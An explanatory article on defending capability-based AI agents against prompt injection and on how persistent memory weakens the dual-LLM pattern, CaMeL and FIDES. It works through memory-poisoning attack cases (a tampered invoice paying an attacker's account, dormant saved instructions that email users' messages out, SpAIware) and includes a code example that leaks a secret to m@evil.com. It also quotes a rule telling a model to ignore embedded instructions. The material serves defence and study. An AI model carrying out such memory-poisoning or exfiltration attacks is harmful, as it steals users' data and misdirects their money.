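# Persistent memory in capability-based AI agents

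## What is a capability-based agent, and what does memory change?

An AI agent is a program in which a large language model calls software tools to do things such as search a mailbox, open web pages, edit files or send money. In a capability-based agent, ordinary software makes the final decision on each tool call. It records where every piece of data came from and who may see it, and it blocks calls that would break a rule about that data. Researchers developed this approach to defend against prompt injection, an attack that hides text in something the agent reads, such as an email, to make the model treat it as an instruction from the user. Well-known designs include the dual-LLM pattern, which divides the agent between two models, and CaMeL and FIDES, which add data tracking.

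These systems were mostly designed with a single task in mind, in which the user asks for something, the agent does it, and whatever the agent learned is then lost. Many agents now have persistent memory, which is anything an agent stores in one session and can read in a later one. A guarantee about one task does not automatically cover a value that the agent stores during that task and uses in a later one.

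### How a tool-using agent works

A language model predicts what comes next in a text, one token (a word or a piece of a word) at a time. It cannot send an email on its own. Developers turn it into an agent by wrapping it in a program that supplies the user's request and a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the arguments it takes. When the model writes a tool call in the agreed format, the program runs the tool, adds the result to the text and calls the model again. This repeats until the model writes a final answer.

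Suppose a user asks for the latest invoice from a supplier named Acme. The model writes a call to the email search tool, and the program adds the matching emails to the model's context, which is all the text it works from. The model picks one and writes a call to open the attachment, and the program adds the invoice too. The next tool call depends on the whole context, which now contains the developer's instructions, the user's request, emails from several strangers and a document from outside the company.

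The program wraps each part of the text in role tags, which identify it as coming from the developer, the user, the model or a tool. Developers train models to obey the user's text and to treat tool output only as information.

### Why a model cannot reliably separate instructions from data

Older software solved a similar problem. Websites query databases in a language called SQL, and a site that inserts a visitor's text directly into a query lets the visitor add commands. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the visitor's text separately, so that the database engine can never interpret the text as a command. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, explains why this fix does not carry over to language models. A recruiter's system might ask a model to score a CV in which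 the candidate has hidden a line telling the model to approve it. A database engine handles commands and data differently, but the model handles both the recruiter's request and the hidden line as text from which to predict the next token.

Role tags have only a weak effect on how a model represents the source of a text. In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) wrapped identical copies of ordinary web passages in each of five role tags, then trained a simple classifier to identify the role from the model's internal activations. Because the passages were identical, the classifier could learn only the effect of the tags. The researchers then applied it to a conversation about gardening, where passages of the model's own reasoning scored 85% on average as "own reasoning". These passages still scored 83% with all the tags removed and 85% with the whole conversation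 wrapped in user tags, because the style of the writing overrode the tags.

The effect also appears in behaviour. Ye and colleagues forged passages of reasoning to justify harmful requests, and 61% of these attacks worked. When a second model rephrased the same arguments in a different style, 10% worked. In 1,000 attempts to make an agent leak data, the success rate rose from 2% where measured role confusion was lowest to 70% where it was highest.

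Current language models convert every token into a list of numbers and place instructions and data in the same numerical space. *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in such a model unless something enforces a separation between the two. The paper compares this to ordinary computers, which keep programs and data in one memory and have no way to distinguish them without outside help. Some processors now provide that help by tagging regions of memory by purpose and enforcing the tags. For language models, *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) lists delimiters, role labels and written warnings as useful engineering practices that fall short of a hard security boundary.

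The proof does not show how often attacks succeed, and by mid-2026 they rarely succeeded against the best models. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*, no attack succeeded against Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios when a scanner for hidden instructions and a filter that blocks dangerous actions were also running. Without these two defences, 3.7% of attacks succeeded. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) gives success rates of about 0.05% for attacks typed directly to the GPT-5.6 Sol model and 3.77% for attacks hidden in content that the agent processes.

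A success rate of a few percent is still high for an agent that can move money, because an attacker can try again by sending another email. If each attempt succeeded independently 3.77% of the time, twenty attempts would give the attacker a 54% chance of at least one success. Real attempts are probably less independent, because a model that resists one message tends to resist near copies of it. On a test by the security firm Gray Swan, the success rate against Opus 5 after 15 attempts was 2.0%.

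David C applies an older security idea, the confused deputy, to language models. A confused deputy is a program with privileges that someone without them tricks into acting on their behalf. Programmers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C regards a language model as inherently confusable and so recommends deterministic safeguards outside the model to limit what the system can do. One rule of thumb in the post is that a model should drop to the privileges of whoever wrote the text it is processing, so an agent reading a stranger's email would have no more power than the stranger.

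### Control flow and data flow

An attacker can target an agent's control flow or its data flow. Control flow is which actions the agent takes and in what order, and data flow is which values those actions receive. When an agent pays an invoice, for example, the control flow is finding the invoice, reading it and making the payment. The data flow includes the account number and the amount.

Capability-based agents protect control flow by dividing the work between two models. A privileged planner takes the user's request, decides the steps and can call tools, but never sees untrusted text. A quarantined model reads that text but has no tools. The planner might write a short program that opens an invoice, has the quarantined model extract the account number, and pays that account. Ordinary software then runs the program. If the invoice contains a hidden instruction, it reaches only the quarantined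 model, which can't carry it out.

This leaves the data flow exposed. In *SPA*, a design for agents that keep memory between requests, Girrens and Wang (2026) point out that an attack on data flow needs no malicious instruction. The agent can carry out exactly the steps the user wanted and still send the money to an account the attacker chose. The designs therefore also track where values came from and check them before any consequential action, meaning a tool call with effects outside the agent, such as a payment, message or deletion.

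### Two meanings of "capability"

In the older, operating-systems sense, a capability is an unforgeable reference that both names an object and grants the right to use it. A program that holds a capability for one file can open that file but cannot open another by guessing its name, because a name alone grants no rights. *Always-On Agents* (Ding, Nannapaneni et al., 2026), a survey of agents with persistent memory, draws on this tradition when it describes the right to influence an action as an explicit, revocable grant.

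CaMeL uses "capability" to mean a record, attached to a value such as an account number or a sentence, of where the value came from and who may receive it. "Capability tag" is a better name for this record because, unlike an operating-system capability, it gives its holder no power. Instead, software checks the tag before passing the value to a tool. The term "capability-based agent" comes from CaMeL's sense, but both senses matter once an agent has memory. An agent that stores an operating-system capability needs to know later whether it should still work, and an agent that stores a tagged value needs to retrieve the tag along with it.

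### Labels and the rule for combining them

FIDES and SPA use a more uniform mark called a label, which has two parts. The integrity part records how much the data's source can be trusted, and the confidentiality part records who may read the data. In the simplest version, each part has two levels, so a value is either trusted or untrusted and either public or private.

The rule for combining labels is that a result is at least as confidential as its most confidential input and no more trusted than its least trusted one. With confidentiality levels $c$ and integrity levels $i$ on ordered scales,

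$$(c_1, i_1) \sqcup (c_2, i_2) = (\max(c_1, c_2),\ \min(i_1, i_2)).$$

Suppose the user types a payment reference, which is trusted, and the agent takes an account number from an emailed invoice, which is untrusted. The payment order that combines them is untrusted. Combining data can make the result more confidential but less trusted, because a document with one private line is unfit to publish and a payment order with one forged number is unfit to execute.

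Each tool has a policy that sets the highest confidentiality and the lowest integrity its inputs may have. A payment tool might require trusted inputs, while a web search tool might allow untrusted text as long as it is public. The software compares the label on the inputs with the policy and blocks the call if the inputs violate either limit.

Anything derived from an untrusted value is also labeled untrusted. This spread is usually called taint. A summary of an untrusted email is untrusted, however neutral it sounds. Taint also passes through decisions. If an untrusted email determines whether a payment happens, Girrens and Wang's scheme treats the payment as untrusted even if the user typed the account number and the amount.

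### What an agent stores

Ding and colleagues describe the usual agent as episodic: it finishes a task and resets. The reset makes safety easier to reason about, because clean input and authorised tool calls within one task are enough. An agent with persistent memory loses that convenience, since anything it kept can shape what it does next. What it keeps takes several forms:

- Facts about the user, such as a home city, a preferred airline or a liking for quick checkout.
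- Notes that the agent writes while it works, for instance that Acme's invoice falls due on the 15th.
- Conversation summaries, which the agent loads later in place of the full transcript.
- Memory files, which are documents that the agent opens and edits, like a coding assistant's page of conventions for one project.
- Saved procedures: plans or scripts that worked once and that the agent can run again.
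- Searchable stores, databases of past messages, documents and notes from which software fetches the entries that best match the current request.

Different forms of memory carry different risks. A wrong fact is information the model can weigh, whereas running a poisoned procedure has effects in the world. Preferences can also drift. Ding and colleagues describe how an agent can come to treat a preference for fast checkout, built up over many ordinary conversations, as permission to skip confirmation on a purchase. In their survey, stored state includes not only memories but also open task lists, access tokens and conditions that make an agent act unprompted.

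Every form of memory passes through three stages. In writing, the agent turns something from the current session into a stored record, and the record's origin is either kept with it or lost. In retrieval, the agent brings the record back in a later session, perhaps into the planner's context. In acting, a tool call uses the record or follows from it. Among the 435 works that Ding and colleagues coded, 269 deal with retrieval, 200 with writing and 141 with acting. Only 87 touch on validation, a check on a record between its writing and its use, and 72 deal with what permits a stored item to influence an action. These counts overlap and measure attention rather than quality, but researchers have clearly given more attention to making memory work than to deciding what it may do.

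### The Monday invoice and the Tuesday payment

Girrens and Wang give an example. On Monday a user asks an agent to fetch an invoice from Acme and keep the details for later. An attacker has put their own account number and a hidden instruction in the invoice. The agent saves it, and nothing bad happens that day. On Tuesday the user says "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday".

An ordinary agent retrieves the saved invoice and passes its text to the planner, which may follow the hidden instruction and add a step the user never asked for, such as forwarding last month's bank statements to an outside address. Girrens and Wang call this a delayed planning attack. A filter on Tuesday's incoming messages would not catch it, because the user's request is genuine and the harmful text is already in the agent's memory.

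A false account number in a saved invoice is dangerous even when the plan is correct. If the planner never sees the invoice and writes only "look up the saved invoice and pay the account on it", the agent follows the steps the user wanted but pays the attacker. Girrens and Wang call this a delayed execution attack. Searching the memory for suspicious instructions would not catch it, because an account number is not an instruction and the false one looks like any other.

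Within a single task, software could track the account number from the invoice to the payment tool and see that it was untrusted. But the task ends between Monday and Tuesday, and the software's working record is lost unless the agent stored the "untrusted" label with the number. Without the label, the agent recalls the number on Tuesday as an ordinary memory, in response to a request from a user the system rightly trusts. That user has the authority to request a payment to Acme, but may never have looked at the account number.

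If the label does survive, a payment tool that requires trusted inputs will refuse the transfer. It will also refuse to pay Acme's real invoices, because they arrive by the same email channel and carry the same untrusted label.

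## What do the dual-LLM pattern and the published design patterns do with stored state?

The dual-LLM pattern protects the agent by never letting the planner see untrusted text. It has no labels, so it would not refuse either the false invoice or the real one. Simon Willison, a programmer who writes about AI security, proposed the pattern in 2023, and in 2025 a group of researchers included it in a catalogue of six design patterns. Neither he nor the researchers explained what an agent should do with stored data after a task ends. Whether the patterns' protections still hold on Tuesday depends on the form in which the agent stored Monday's invoice.

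### Willison's proposal

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) started from the rule that a model that reads untrusted text must not be able to take any action an attacker could abuse. If the text might mix with private data, the model must also be unable to produce outbound links or images, because a web address can carry stolen data and merely displaying an image sends its address to the attacker's server. An assistant under these rules could do very little, so Willison split it into two models and applied the rules to only one.

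Willison calls the planner the privileged model and expects that the quarantined model could "go rogue at any moment". A third component, the controller, is ordinary software that runs the tools and moves data between the models. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the work proceeds as follows:

1. The controller passes the request to the privileged model.
2. The privileged model asks for the latest email and names the result `$VAR1`.
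3. The controller fetches the email and stores it under that name, without showing it to the privileged model.
4. The privileged model asks the quarantined model to summarise `$VAR1`. The controller swaps the name for the email's text, runs the quarantined model and stores the summary as `$VAR2`.
5. The controller tells the privileged model only that the summary is ready. The privileged model writes a reply containing the name `$VAR2`, and the controller fills in the summary when it displays the reply to the user.

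The privileged model handles the email purely by reference, meaning that it passes the name around without seeing the content.

Willison lets the privileged model see the quarantined model's output only when software can verify it. For example, if the only permitted answers are "invoice", "receipt" and "other", the controller can check that the output is exactly one of those words. An attacker might cause the wrong choice but cannot insert an instruction. Free text is never allowed. Willison also warns about chaining models, because a model that has read an injected instruction may repeat it in its output. A summary of an untrusted email is therefore as dangerous to the privileged model as the email.

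Willison called the solution "pretty bad". It makes an assistant harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that leaks untrusted text to the privileged model undoes the protection. The text that the controller displays could also persuade the user to copy private data and paste it into an attacker's website.

Researchers at Google DeepMind later described another flaw, which Willison acknowledged in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025). In their example, a user asks an agent to find Bob's email address in meeting notes and send him a document. The quarantined model extracts the address, but if an attacker has tampered with the notes, it may return the attacker's address instead. The privileged model then sends the document there without seeing the address. The false account number in the Acme invoice works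 the same way.

In Willison's example, the controller keeps the variables while it handles one request. Willison does not discuss whether to keep them afterward. An assistant that kept them for later sessions would have to save both the values and the rule that the planner may not read them.

### The six design patterns

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, think it unlikely that general-purpose agents built on current language models can offer reliable safety guarantees. Their patterns instead limit what agents can do in order to protect them. All six follow the principle that, once an agent has taken in untrusted input, it must be "impossible for that input to trigger any consequential actions". The agent's outputs should also not cause problems later, for example by "manipulating future agent behavior". This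 would happen if an agent saved an invoice containing malicious instructions on Monday and followed them on Tuesday, so the principle extends to persistent memory even though the patterns were not designed for it.

In the action-selector pattern, the model translates a request into one or more predefined actions. A customer service chatbot, for example, might only be able to fetch a link to the customer's last order or direct the customer to the password settings. The model never sees the results of these actions, so instructions in the data they touch cannot reach it.

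In the plan-then-execute pattern, the model sees tool results, but it fixes the list of tool calls before any tool runs. Given the request "send today's schedule to my boss John Doe", it plans to read the calendar and then email John. An instruction hidden in a calendar entry cannot add a step, though it can change the body of the email. In *Architecting Resilient LLM Agents*, Del Rosario, Krawiecka and Schroeder de Witt (2025) also describe the plan as fixed before the agent reads outside data, and they give a similar warning about data passed between steps. An agent that summarises a report from a website and emails it to a chief executive may deliver a phishing message while following its plan exactly.

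The map-reduce pattern gives each document to a separate, isolated model. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues use the example of an agent that finds this month's invoices among a user's files and emails them to the accounting department. One model per file answers only whether the file is an invoice, and a final step gathers the matching files and sends the email. A malicious file can cause its model to count it as an invoice but cannot affect how the agent treats other files. The final step either uses no language model or receives only answers that software has checked, such as a yes, a no or a number.

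Beurer-Kellner and colleagues treat map-reduce as a special case of Willison's dual-LLM pattern. They say the quarantined model's results are stored in a "memory" that the privileged model can use only by reference. This memory holds the current task's variables and is not persistent memory in the sense used here.

Code-then-execute extends the same idea. The planner writes a complete program that can call tools and quarantined models, and ordinary software runs it. CaMeL is an example.

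The context-minimization pattern addresses attacks in the user's own message, which the planning patterns don't prevent. For example, a customer might ask a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and add text designed to get a large discount. The agent turns the message into a database query, then removes the message from the model's context before the model writes its reply.

### Stored data in the case studies

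Beurer-Kellner and colleagues apply the patterns to ten kinds of agent, including an email assistant, a résumé screener and a coding assistant. None of these agents saves what it learned in one session for use in another. Their appendix of general good practice recommends sandboxes, strict output formats, limited permissions, user confirmation and attribution of outputs to sources, but has no advice on persistent memory. The paper does not specify who may write to an agent's memory, whether a stored value should keep a record of its origin, or whether a later planner may read it.

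Several case studies involve data stored earlier, and the researchers judge its safety by who could have changed it. For an agent that answers questions from databases, they treat any database that other people can modify as a possible source of prompt injections. They recommend that the agent process query results with code and keep them away from the model, although the agent then can't judge whether the results answer the question. For a furniture retailer's chatbot, they consider the company's internal knowledge base low-risk as long as it excludes product reviews, partly because the company could probably trace an employee who planted an attack. They assume that medication leaflets are safe because regulators supervise the pharmaceutical industry closely.

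An agent's own memory is hard to classify by this method. Only the agent writes to it, so it resembles an internal knowledge base, but what the agent writes may come from anyone who can email the user. It is safer to treat the memory as a database that outsiders can modify, because an attacker can get text into it without write access.

Luca Beurer-Kellner and Florian Tramèr, who co-wrote the catalogue, later worked on an attack that exploits this. For *Trojan Hippo Bench*, Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) built an ordinary email assistant with persistent memory and sent it emails containing hidden instructions. The assistant saved an instruction to memory, where it stayed inactive until the user mentioned a sensitive topic such as tax or health. The assistant then emailed the user's message to the attacker. They used an automated search to improve each attack email over up to 40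 rounds. With no memory defences, and 100 harmless sessions between when the instruction was saved and when it was triggered, the attack succeeded up to 100% of the time against Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro and up to 85% against OpenAI's GPT-5-mini.

Das and colleagues conclude in their review of earlier work that the dual-LLM pattern and related defences do not close "the persistent memory gap". Their experiments do not test this directly, because the assistant they attacked used none of the patterns. The results show how dangerous stored text can be to a planner that reads it, but not how a dual-LLM agent with saved variables would fare.

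### The patterns and Tuesday's payment

The agent might have stored the Acme invoice, with its false account number and hidden instruction, in one of these forms:

- As a variable, so that the controller holds the invoice and Tuesday's planner receives only a name for it.
- As a summary, which a model wrote after reading the invoice and which Tuesday's planner reads.
- As text, which software copies from memory into the planner's context.

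A summary that the controller keeps hidden from the planner counts as a variable. The table applies each pattern's definition to these cases and shows whether the pattern's guarantee still holds on Tuesday.

| Pattern | Guarantee within one task | Variable | Summary | Text in the planner's context |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Action-selector | Results never reach the model that chooses actions | Holds | Fails, though the attacker can trigger only predefined actions | Fails, with the same limit |
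| Plan-then-execute | Untrusted data cannot change the list of steps | Holds | Fails | Fails |
| Map-reduce | A document can affect only its own result | Holds | Holds for a checked yes, no or number; fails for free text | Fails |
| Dual LLM | The planner never sees untrusted text | Holds | Holds for a choice from a fixed list; fails for free text | Fails |
| Code-then-execute | Untrusted data cannot change the program | Holds | Fails for free text | Fails |
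| Context-minimization | The user's message cannot shape the reply | Does not cover the invoice | Does not cover the invoice; a saved summary may bring back a deleted message | Does not cover the invoice; a saved transcript brings the message back |

#### Variables

Storing the invoice as a variable preserves the most protection, because Tuesday's planner, like Monday's, receives only the variable's name. This works only if the name is also safe. A name taken from the user's request, such as "Acme invoice", is harmless, but one that the quarantined model copied from the invoice's subject line could contain an instruction.

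The controller must also be the only component that can write to the store. Dongol (2026), in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, proves this kind of result with Isabelle/HOL, software that checks mathematical proofs. In one example, an agent reads a secret and an attacker's email, then sends the email back to the attacker. The email contains a small program that calls no tools but overwrites the variable holding the email with the secret, so the message the agent sends contains the secret. The leak disappears if the system discards the injected program's writes.

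Even where a guarantee is marked "holds" in the table, the agent still pays the attacker, because the guarantees cover the agent's steps but not the values those steps use. A code-then-execute system that tracks where values came from could stop the payment only if the origin label from Monday was still attached to the stored value.

Stored variables can also leak private data. In another of Dongol's examples, a dual-LLM agent without tags gives its quarantined model both the user's private notes and an attacker's email and asks for a reply. An injection in the email makes the quarantined model quote the notes, and the planner sends the reply without seeing it. Within a single task, only the notes that the task needs are at risk. With persistent memory, a careless plan could also mix notes from earlier sessions with a stranger's email.

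#### Summaries

Willison's rule forbids the planner to read a free-text summary of untrusted content, but some later designs called "dual LLM" allow it. *ORBIT* (2026), a framework for testing the safety of AI agents, includes a defence in which a quarantined model summarises each tool result and the privileged model reads the summary. The quarantined model's prompt tells it to stick to facts, ignore any instructions in the content and avoid long quotations. This protection depends on a language model following its instructions while it reads text that an attacker wrote, a dependence the dual-LLM pattern is meant to avoid. If the agent saves such a summary, every later planner that loads it is exposed to the same risk. *Zombie Agents* (2026), which attacked agents through their long-term memory, found that summarising or shortening stored content did not reliably remove malicious instructions.

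Narrow formats are safer. Del Rosario and colleagues suggest that the quarantined model extract information into a strict, data-only format for the planner. For the invoice, this could mean an amount, a due date and a digits-only account number. Software can check these fields, and it is hard to hide an instruction in a string of digits, but the account number could still be the attacker's.

It is less clear how much text a format can safely allow. For a coding agent that needs to learn about unfamiliar software, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues propose reducing the documentation to a formal description, for example with function names limited to 30 characters. In a blog post named after their paper, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, Willison (2025) wonders whether 30 characters are already too many. An attacker could name a function `run_rm_dash_rf_for_compliance`,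 which suggests a command that deletes files. A free-text "payment notes" field in an invoice summary would give an attacker much more room.

#### Text in the planner's context

Plan-then-execute depends on the agent making its plan before it reads untrusted data. The agent in the example follows that order on both days, but if its memory puts Monday's invoice into the context at the start of Tuesday's session, the planner reads the attacker's words before it plans the payment. Code-then-execute fails for the same reason, because the attacker can influence the program the planner writes. Map-reduce no longer keeps documents separate when software loads several saved ones into one context, where an instruction in one can affect how the model treats the rest. The action-selector pattern limits the damage best, since a misled model can still choose only from the list of predefined actions.

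Dongol's proofs cover agents that follow a fixed plan but whose language model may make extra tool calls after reading untrusted text. A separate program, the monitor, can take tools away. If the monitor removes every tool an injected instruction could call as soon as the agent first reads untrusted content, and never gives those tools back, then an injection reveals nothing about the user's data to the attacker beyond what the plan could have revealed anyway. The theorem covers injections that each make a single call. An agent that handles one request after another needs its tools back. The monitor can safely return them at the start of a new session if that session clears everything the model retained from untrusted content, but retrieval from persistent memory breaks this condition.

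Dongol uses SpAIware, an attack on ChatGPT published in 2024, to illustrate the problem. A web page or document made ChatGPT save an instruction to its long-term memory, and in later conversations ChatGPT displayed images whose web addresses contained the user's messages. In Dongol's model of the attack, the monitor restores the image tool at the start of each session and treats loading the memory as part of starting up, so the tool is available when the saved instruction loads. The guarantee holds again if the monitor treats loading the memory as reading untrusted content and therefore removes both the image tool and the tool that writes to memory.

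The proof covers data leaks but not attacks that make an agent act without leaking anything, such as paying the wrong account. If a developer extended the rule to payments, the monitor would remove the payment tool as soon as the agent loaded the saved invoice, and the agent could not pay Acme. The proof also cannot show whether blocking memory writes after an untrusted read would work as an alternative, because Dongol's model takes the contents of memory as an outside input and does not simulate the agent saving them.

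## How do CaMeL and FIDES track data, and where does the tracking stop?

CaMeL and FIDES build on the dual-LLM pattern by recording where each value came from and checking that record before a tool runs. Researchers at Google DeepMind and ETH Zurich published CaMeL (Capabilities for Machine Learning) in 2025, and a Microsoft team published FIDES (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System) the same year. Either system can block an immediate payment to the false account number in the Acme invoice. If the agent pays the next day, the outcome depends on whether the developer saved the number's origin along with the number.

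### Why a fixed plan is not enough

*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) uses the term control-flow integrity for the property that the dual-LLM pattern aims to provide. An agent has it if its actions stay within a plan that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. Untrusted data can still determine the values used in the plan and which of its branches the agent takes. For example, if the plan is to pay an invoice if it is overdue and file it otherwise, the sender can trigger a payment by choosing the due date but can't add a step to the plan.

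Standard tests mostly miss attacks on values. AgentDojo, a widely used benchmark for prompt injection, has 97 user tasks in simulated office, banking, travel and Slack environments. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025), which introduced FIDES, describes an AgentDojo attack that hides instructions to call particular tools in the data an agent reads. The attack succeeded 152 times against a basic agent but never against a planner that could pass variables to tools without reading their contents, even with no checks on the data.

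That result does not show that separating the planner from untrusted text is enough. The attack works by giving the agent instructions, and the score excludes cases in which injected text changed the wording of a result but not the agent's steps. A score of zero therefore does not show that an agent would refuse to send money to a false account number.

### How CaMeL works

Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, describe CaMeL in detail because their own system extends it. CaMeL handles a request in these steps:

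1. The privileged planner reads the user's request and writes the whole plan as a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and makes the tool calls.
3. Where the plan needs information from untrusted text, the interpreter calls the quarantined model like any other function and stores the answer in a variable.
4. The interpreter attaches a capability tag to every value, including values it computes from other values.
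5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs that tool's policy, a short function that allows or denies the call.

For Monday's request to fetch and remember the Acme invoice, the planner might write this program:

```
email = find_email("latest invoice from Acme")
account = ask_quarantined_model("Extract the account number", email)
save_note("Acme account", account)
```

The planner must know the format of each tool's output because it writes a program to handle output it has not seen. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add a description of the output format to every tool before agents using CaMeL could do reasonably well on their tests. The restricted language leaves out features that would make values hard to track. For example, a plan cannot define its own functions, according to *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026).

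A capability tag records a value's origin as "Sources" and its permitted recipients as "Readers". For a calendar event, the readers might be the user and the people invited. The event's description is trusted only if the user wrote it, so different fields of one event can have different tags. In the program above, the quarantined model produced `account`, but its tag still lists the email as a source.

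A policy receives the name of the tool, the arguments and the arguments' tags. One of CaMeL's policies for the banking tasks allows a password change only if the new password comes from a trusted source.

Girrens and Wang point out that such policies can express more than a comparison of labels, but that the system's security then depends on every tool's policy being correct. If a payment tool's policy does not check the recipient, CaMeL will pay the attacker even though it has tagged the account number correctly.

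### How FIDES works

Like an ordinary agent, a FIDES planner chooses one tool call at a time and receives each result before choosing the next. This makes it more flexible than a planner that writes its whole plan in advance, but it also means that untrusted text could reach the planner partway through a task. FIDES therefore labels the planner's context too, combining the labels of everything in it. If the planner reads one untrusted email, every call it writes afterwards is untrusted.

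Costa and colleagues put labels on messages, tool calls, individual arguments, results and the variables in the datastore. The datastore is everything outside the planner that tools can read or change, such as a mailbox or a calendar. A confidentiality label can be a list of permitted readers. If Ann, Bob and Cat may read one document and Bob, Cat and Dan may read another, only Bob and Cat may read a text that combines them.

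When the planner calls a tool $f$, the result gets the label

$$\ell_{\text{result}} = \ell_{\text{call}} \;\sqcup\; \bigsqcup_{a}\, \ell_a \;\sqcup\; \bigsqcup_{x \in R(f)} \tau(x).$$

Here $\ell_{\text{call}}$ is the label of the planner's decision to make the call, $\ell_a$ is the label of argument $a$, $R(f)$ is the set of datastore variables the tool may read, $\tau(x)$ is the label of variable $x$, and $\sqcup$ combines labels by the usual rule. Any datastore variable the tool may write to also gets the combined label.

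#### Hiding results

Before adding a tool result to the planner's context, FIDES compares the label on each part of the result with the context's current label. If a part would make the context less trusted or more confidential, FIDES stores it in a variable with its label and shows the planner only the variable's name. Otherwise the planner sees the content. In a list of emails, for instance, the planner might read the trusted fields but see only variable names in place of the subjects and bodies. Willison's original pattern would hide the entire list.

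The planner can use a quarantined model to extract information from a hidden variable, and a policy may let the planner read very limited answers, such as yes or no.

#### Checking calls

FIDES allows a consequential call only if the decision to make it and all of its arguments are trusted. A developer can relax this for particular arguments. A messaging tool might require a trusted decision and a trusted recipient but accept a message body that came from a web search.

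A separate confidentiality rule lets information be sent through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is also allowed to read the information. It limits what a successful prompt injection can leak, but does not prevent injection.

In the AgentDojo tests, no attacks succeeded against FIDES with its policy checks on, but 21 succeeded with them off because the planner could open untrusted variables and continue.

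Microsoft released FIDES as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework in May 2026. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. An attacker files a public report with a hidden instruction to read a file of secrets and post it as a comment. If the model obeys and reads the file, the software treats the model's context as private and blocks the public comment.

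### What the tracking misses within one run

Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Write $d_1 =_L d_2$ when two datastores agree on every variable labelled public, and let $g$ be the overall effect that a particular sequence of tool calls has on the datastore. Explicit secrecy requires that

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\implies\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

In other words, for a given sequence of calls, changing only the secret data cannot change any public data.

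The property does not cover implicit flows, in which information leaks through the choice of calls. For example, the planner might read a private bank balance and then send one of two ready-made public messages depending on the balance. Each message is public, so sending it breaks no content rule, but the recipient can infer something about the balance from which message arrives. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger property, non-interference, which would rule out such leaks. They judged it too restrictive because it would essentially forbid an agent that had used a secret-reading tool from then using any tool that writes public data. Their model also excludes side channels such as timing and the length of network packets.

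CaMeL has no comparable proof. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, describe two leaks in it. One depends on a branch that the program does not take, as in this version of a textbook example:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`. CaMeL updates a variable's tag only when the program runs a line that changes the variable, so `rich` remains public. The email goes out only when the balance is high, which reveals the secret. A planner that reads only the user's request has little reason to write such a program, so this is more a gap in CaMeL's guarantees than an easy attack.

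The other leak comes from the ordinary Python loop around the interpreter. The loop tries again when a policy blocks a plan, and nothing tracks it. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, so repeated attempts can reveal all of it. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) also describes leaks through loop counts, error messages and timing. For example, if a program fetches a web page as many times as a secret number, the website's logs reveal the number.

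Garby and colleagues conclude that "a flow-tracking guarantee holds only where the tracking reaches". Their retry loop is a few lines of code outside the interpreter, and persistent memory is usually outside it too.

### Where a run ends

FIDES's formal model contains most of what a persistent memory needs. A memory entry can be a variable in the datastore. If a tool saves an untrusted account number there, the variable gets an untrusted label under the formula above, and any tool that later reads the entry returns an untrusted result.

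The model describes a single planning loop, which starts with a user message and a labelled datastore and returns only the final response and its label. It doesn't return the updated datastore labels, so a developer who wants to keep them for a later loop has to save and reload them.

Explicit secrecy depends on this step because it is defined relative to the labels in place when a run starts. If Tuesday's run carries over Monday's final labels and nothing else, the guarantee covers both runs together, because Monday's run preserves the agreement on public data that Tuesday's run assumes. If Tuesday's run instead starts with a private note labelled public, explicit secrecy can still hold for the run as labelled, but it no longer protects the note.

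CaMeL's interpreter keeps tags only while it runs a single program. When the program calls `save_note`, the interpreter passes the account number to the tool, as in any other tool call. The tag is lost when the program ends unless a developer has written the tool to store the tag too.

In their experiments, Costa and colleagues wrapped each tool in a function that adds labels as the tool reads data. This works for email because much of a message's origin is still visible in the message. A mail server can authenticate the sender's address, and the list of recipients suggests who may read the message. Memory entries are harder to label this way because a bare account number, for example, has no sender, so software cannot work out its label later unless the label was saved with it.

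AgentDojo cannot detect this failure. Girrens and Wang note that its tasks reset the agent's state, so an attack in one request cannot affect a later one.

### What a developer has to store

For the tracking to continue in a new session, the agent has to save more than the value and the word "untrusted":

- **The full label or tag.** In CaMeL, policies also look at the values an argument was computed from, so the stored tag has to include their sources and readers. Readers matter even when an attack is not involved. *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries* (2026) argues that without labels an agent cannot distinguish one user's preferences from a group's confidential playbook, and that leaks between sessions then become the default.
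- **The label of the decision to save.** FIDES's formula includes $\ell_{\text{call}}$ for this purpose. If the planner has read an untrusted email and then saves a note, the note is untrusted, even if every word in it came from the user.
- **The label of any saved context.** If a session resumes an old conversation or loads a summary of it, the context should start with the old conversation's label.
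- **The difference between the user's words and the user's files.** A user might upload Acme's invoice instead of having the agent find it in the mailbox. Tallam and Miller propose a separate tag for values extracted from uploaded files, so that a policy can keep them out of irreversible actions.

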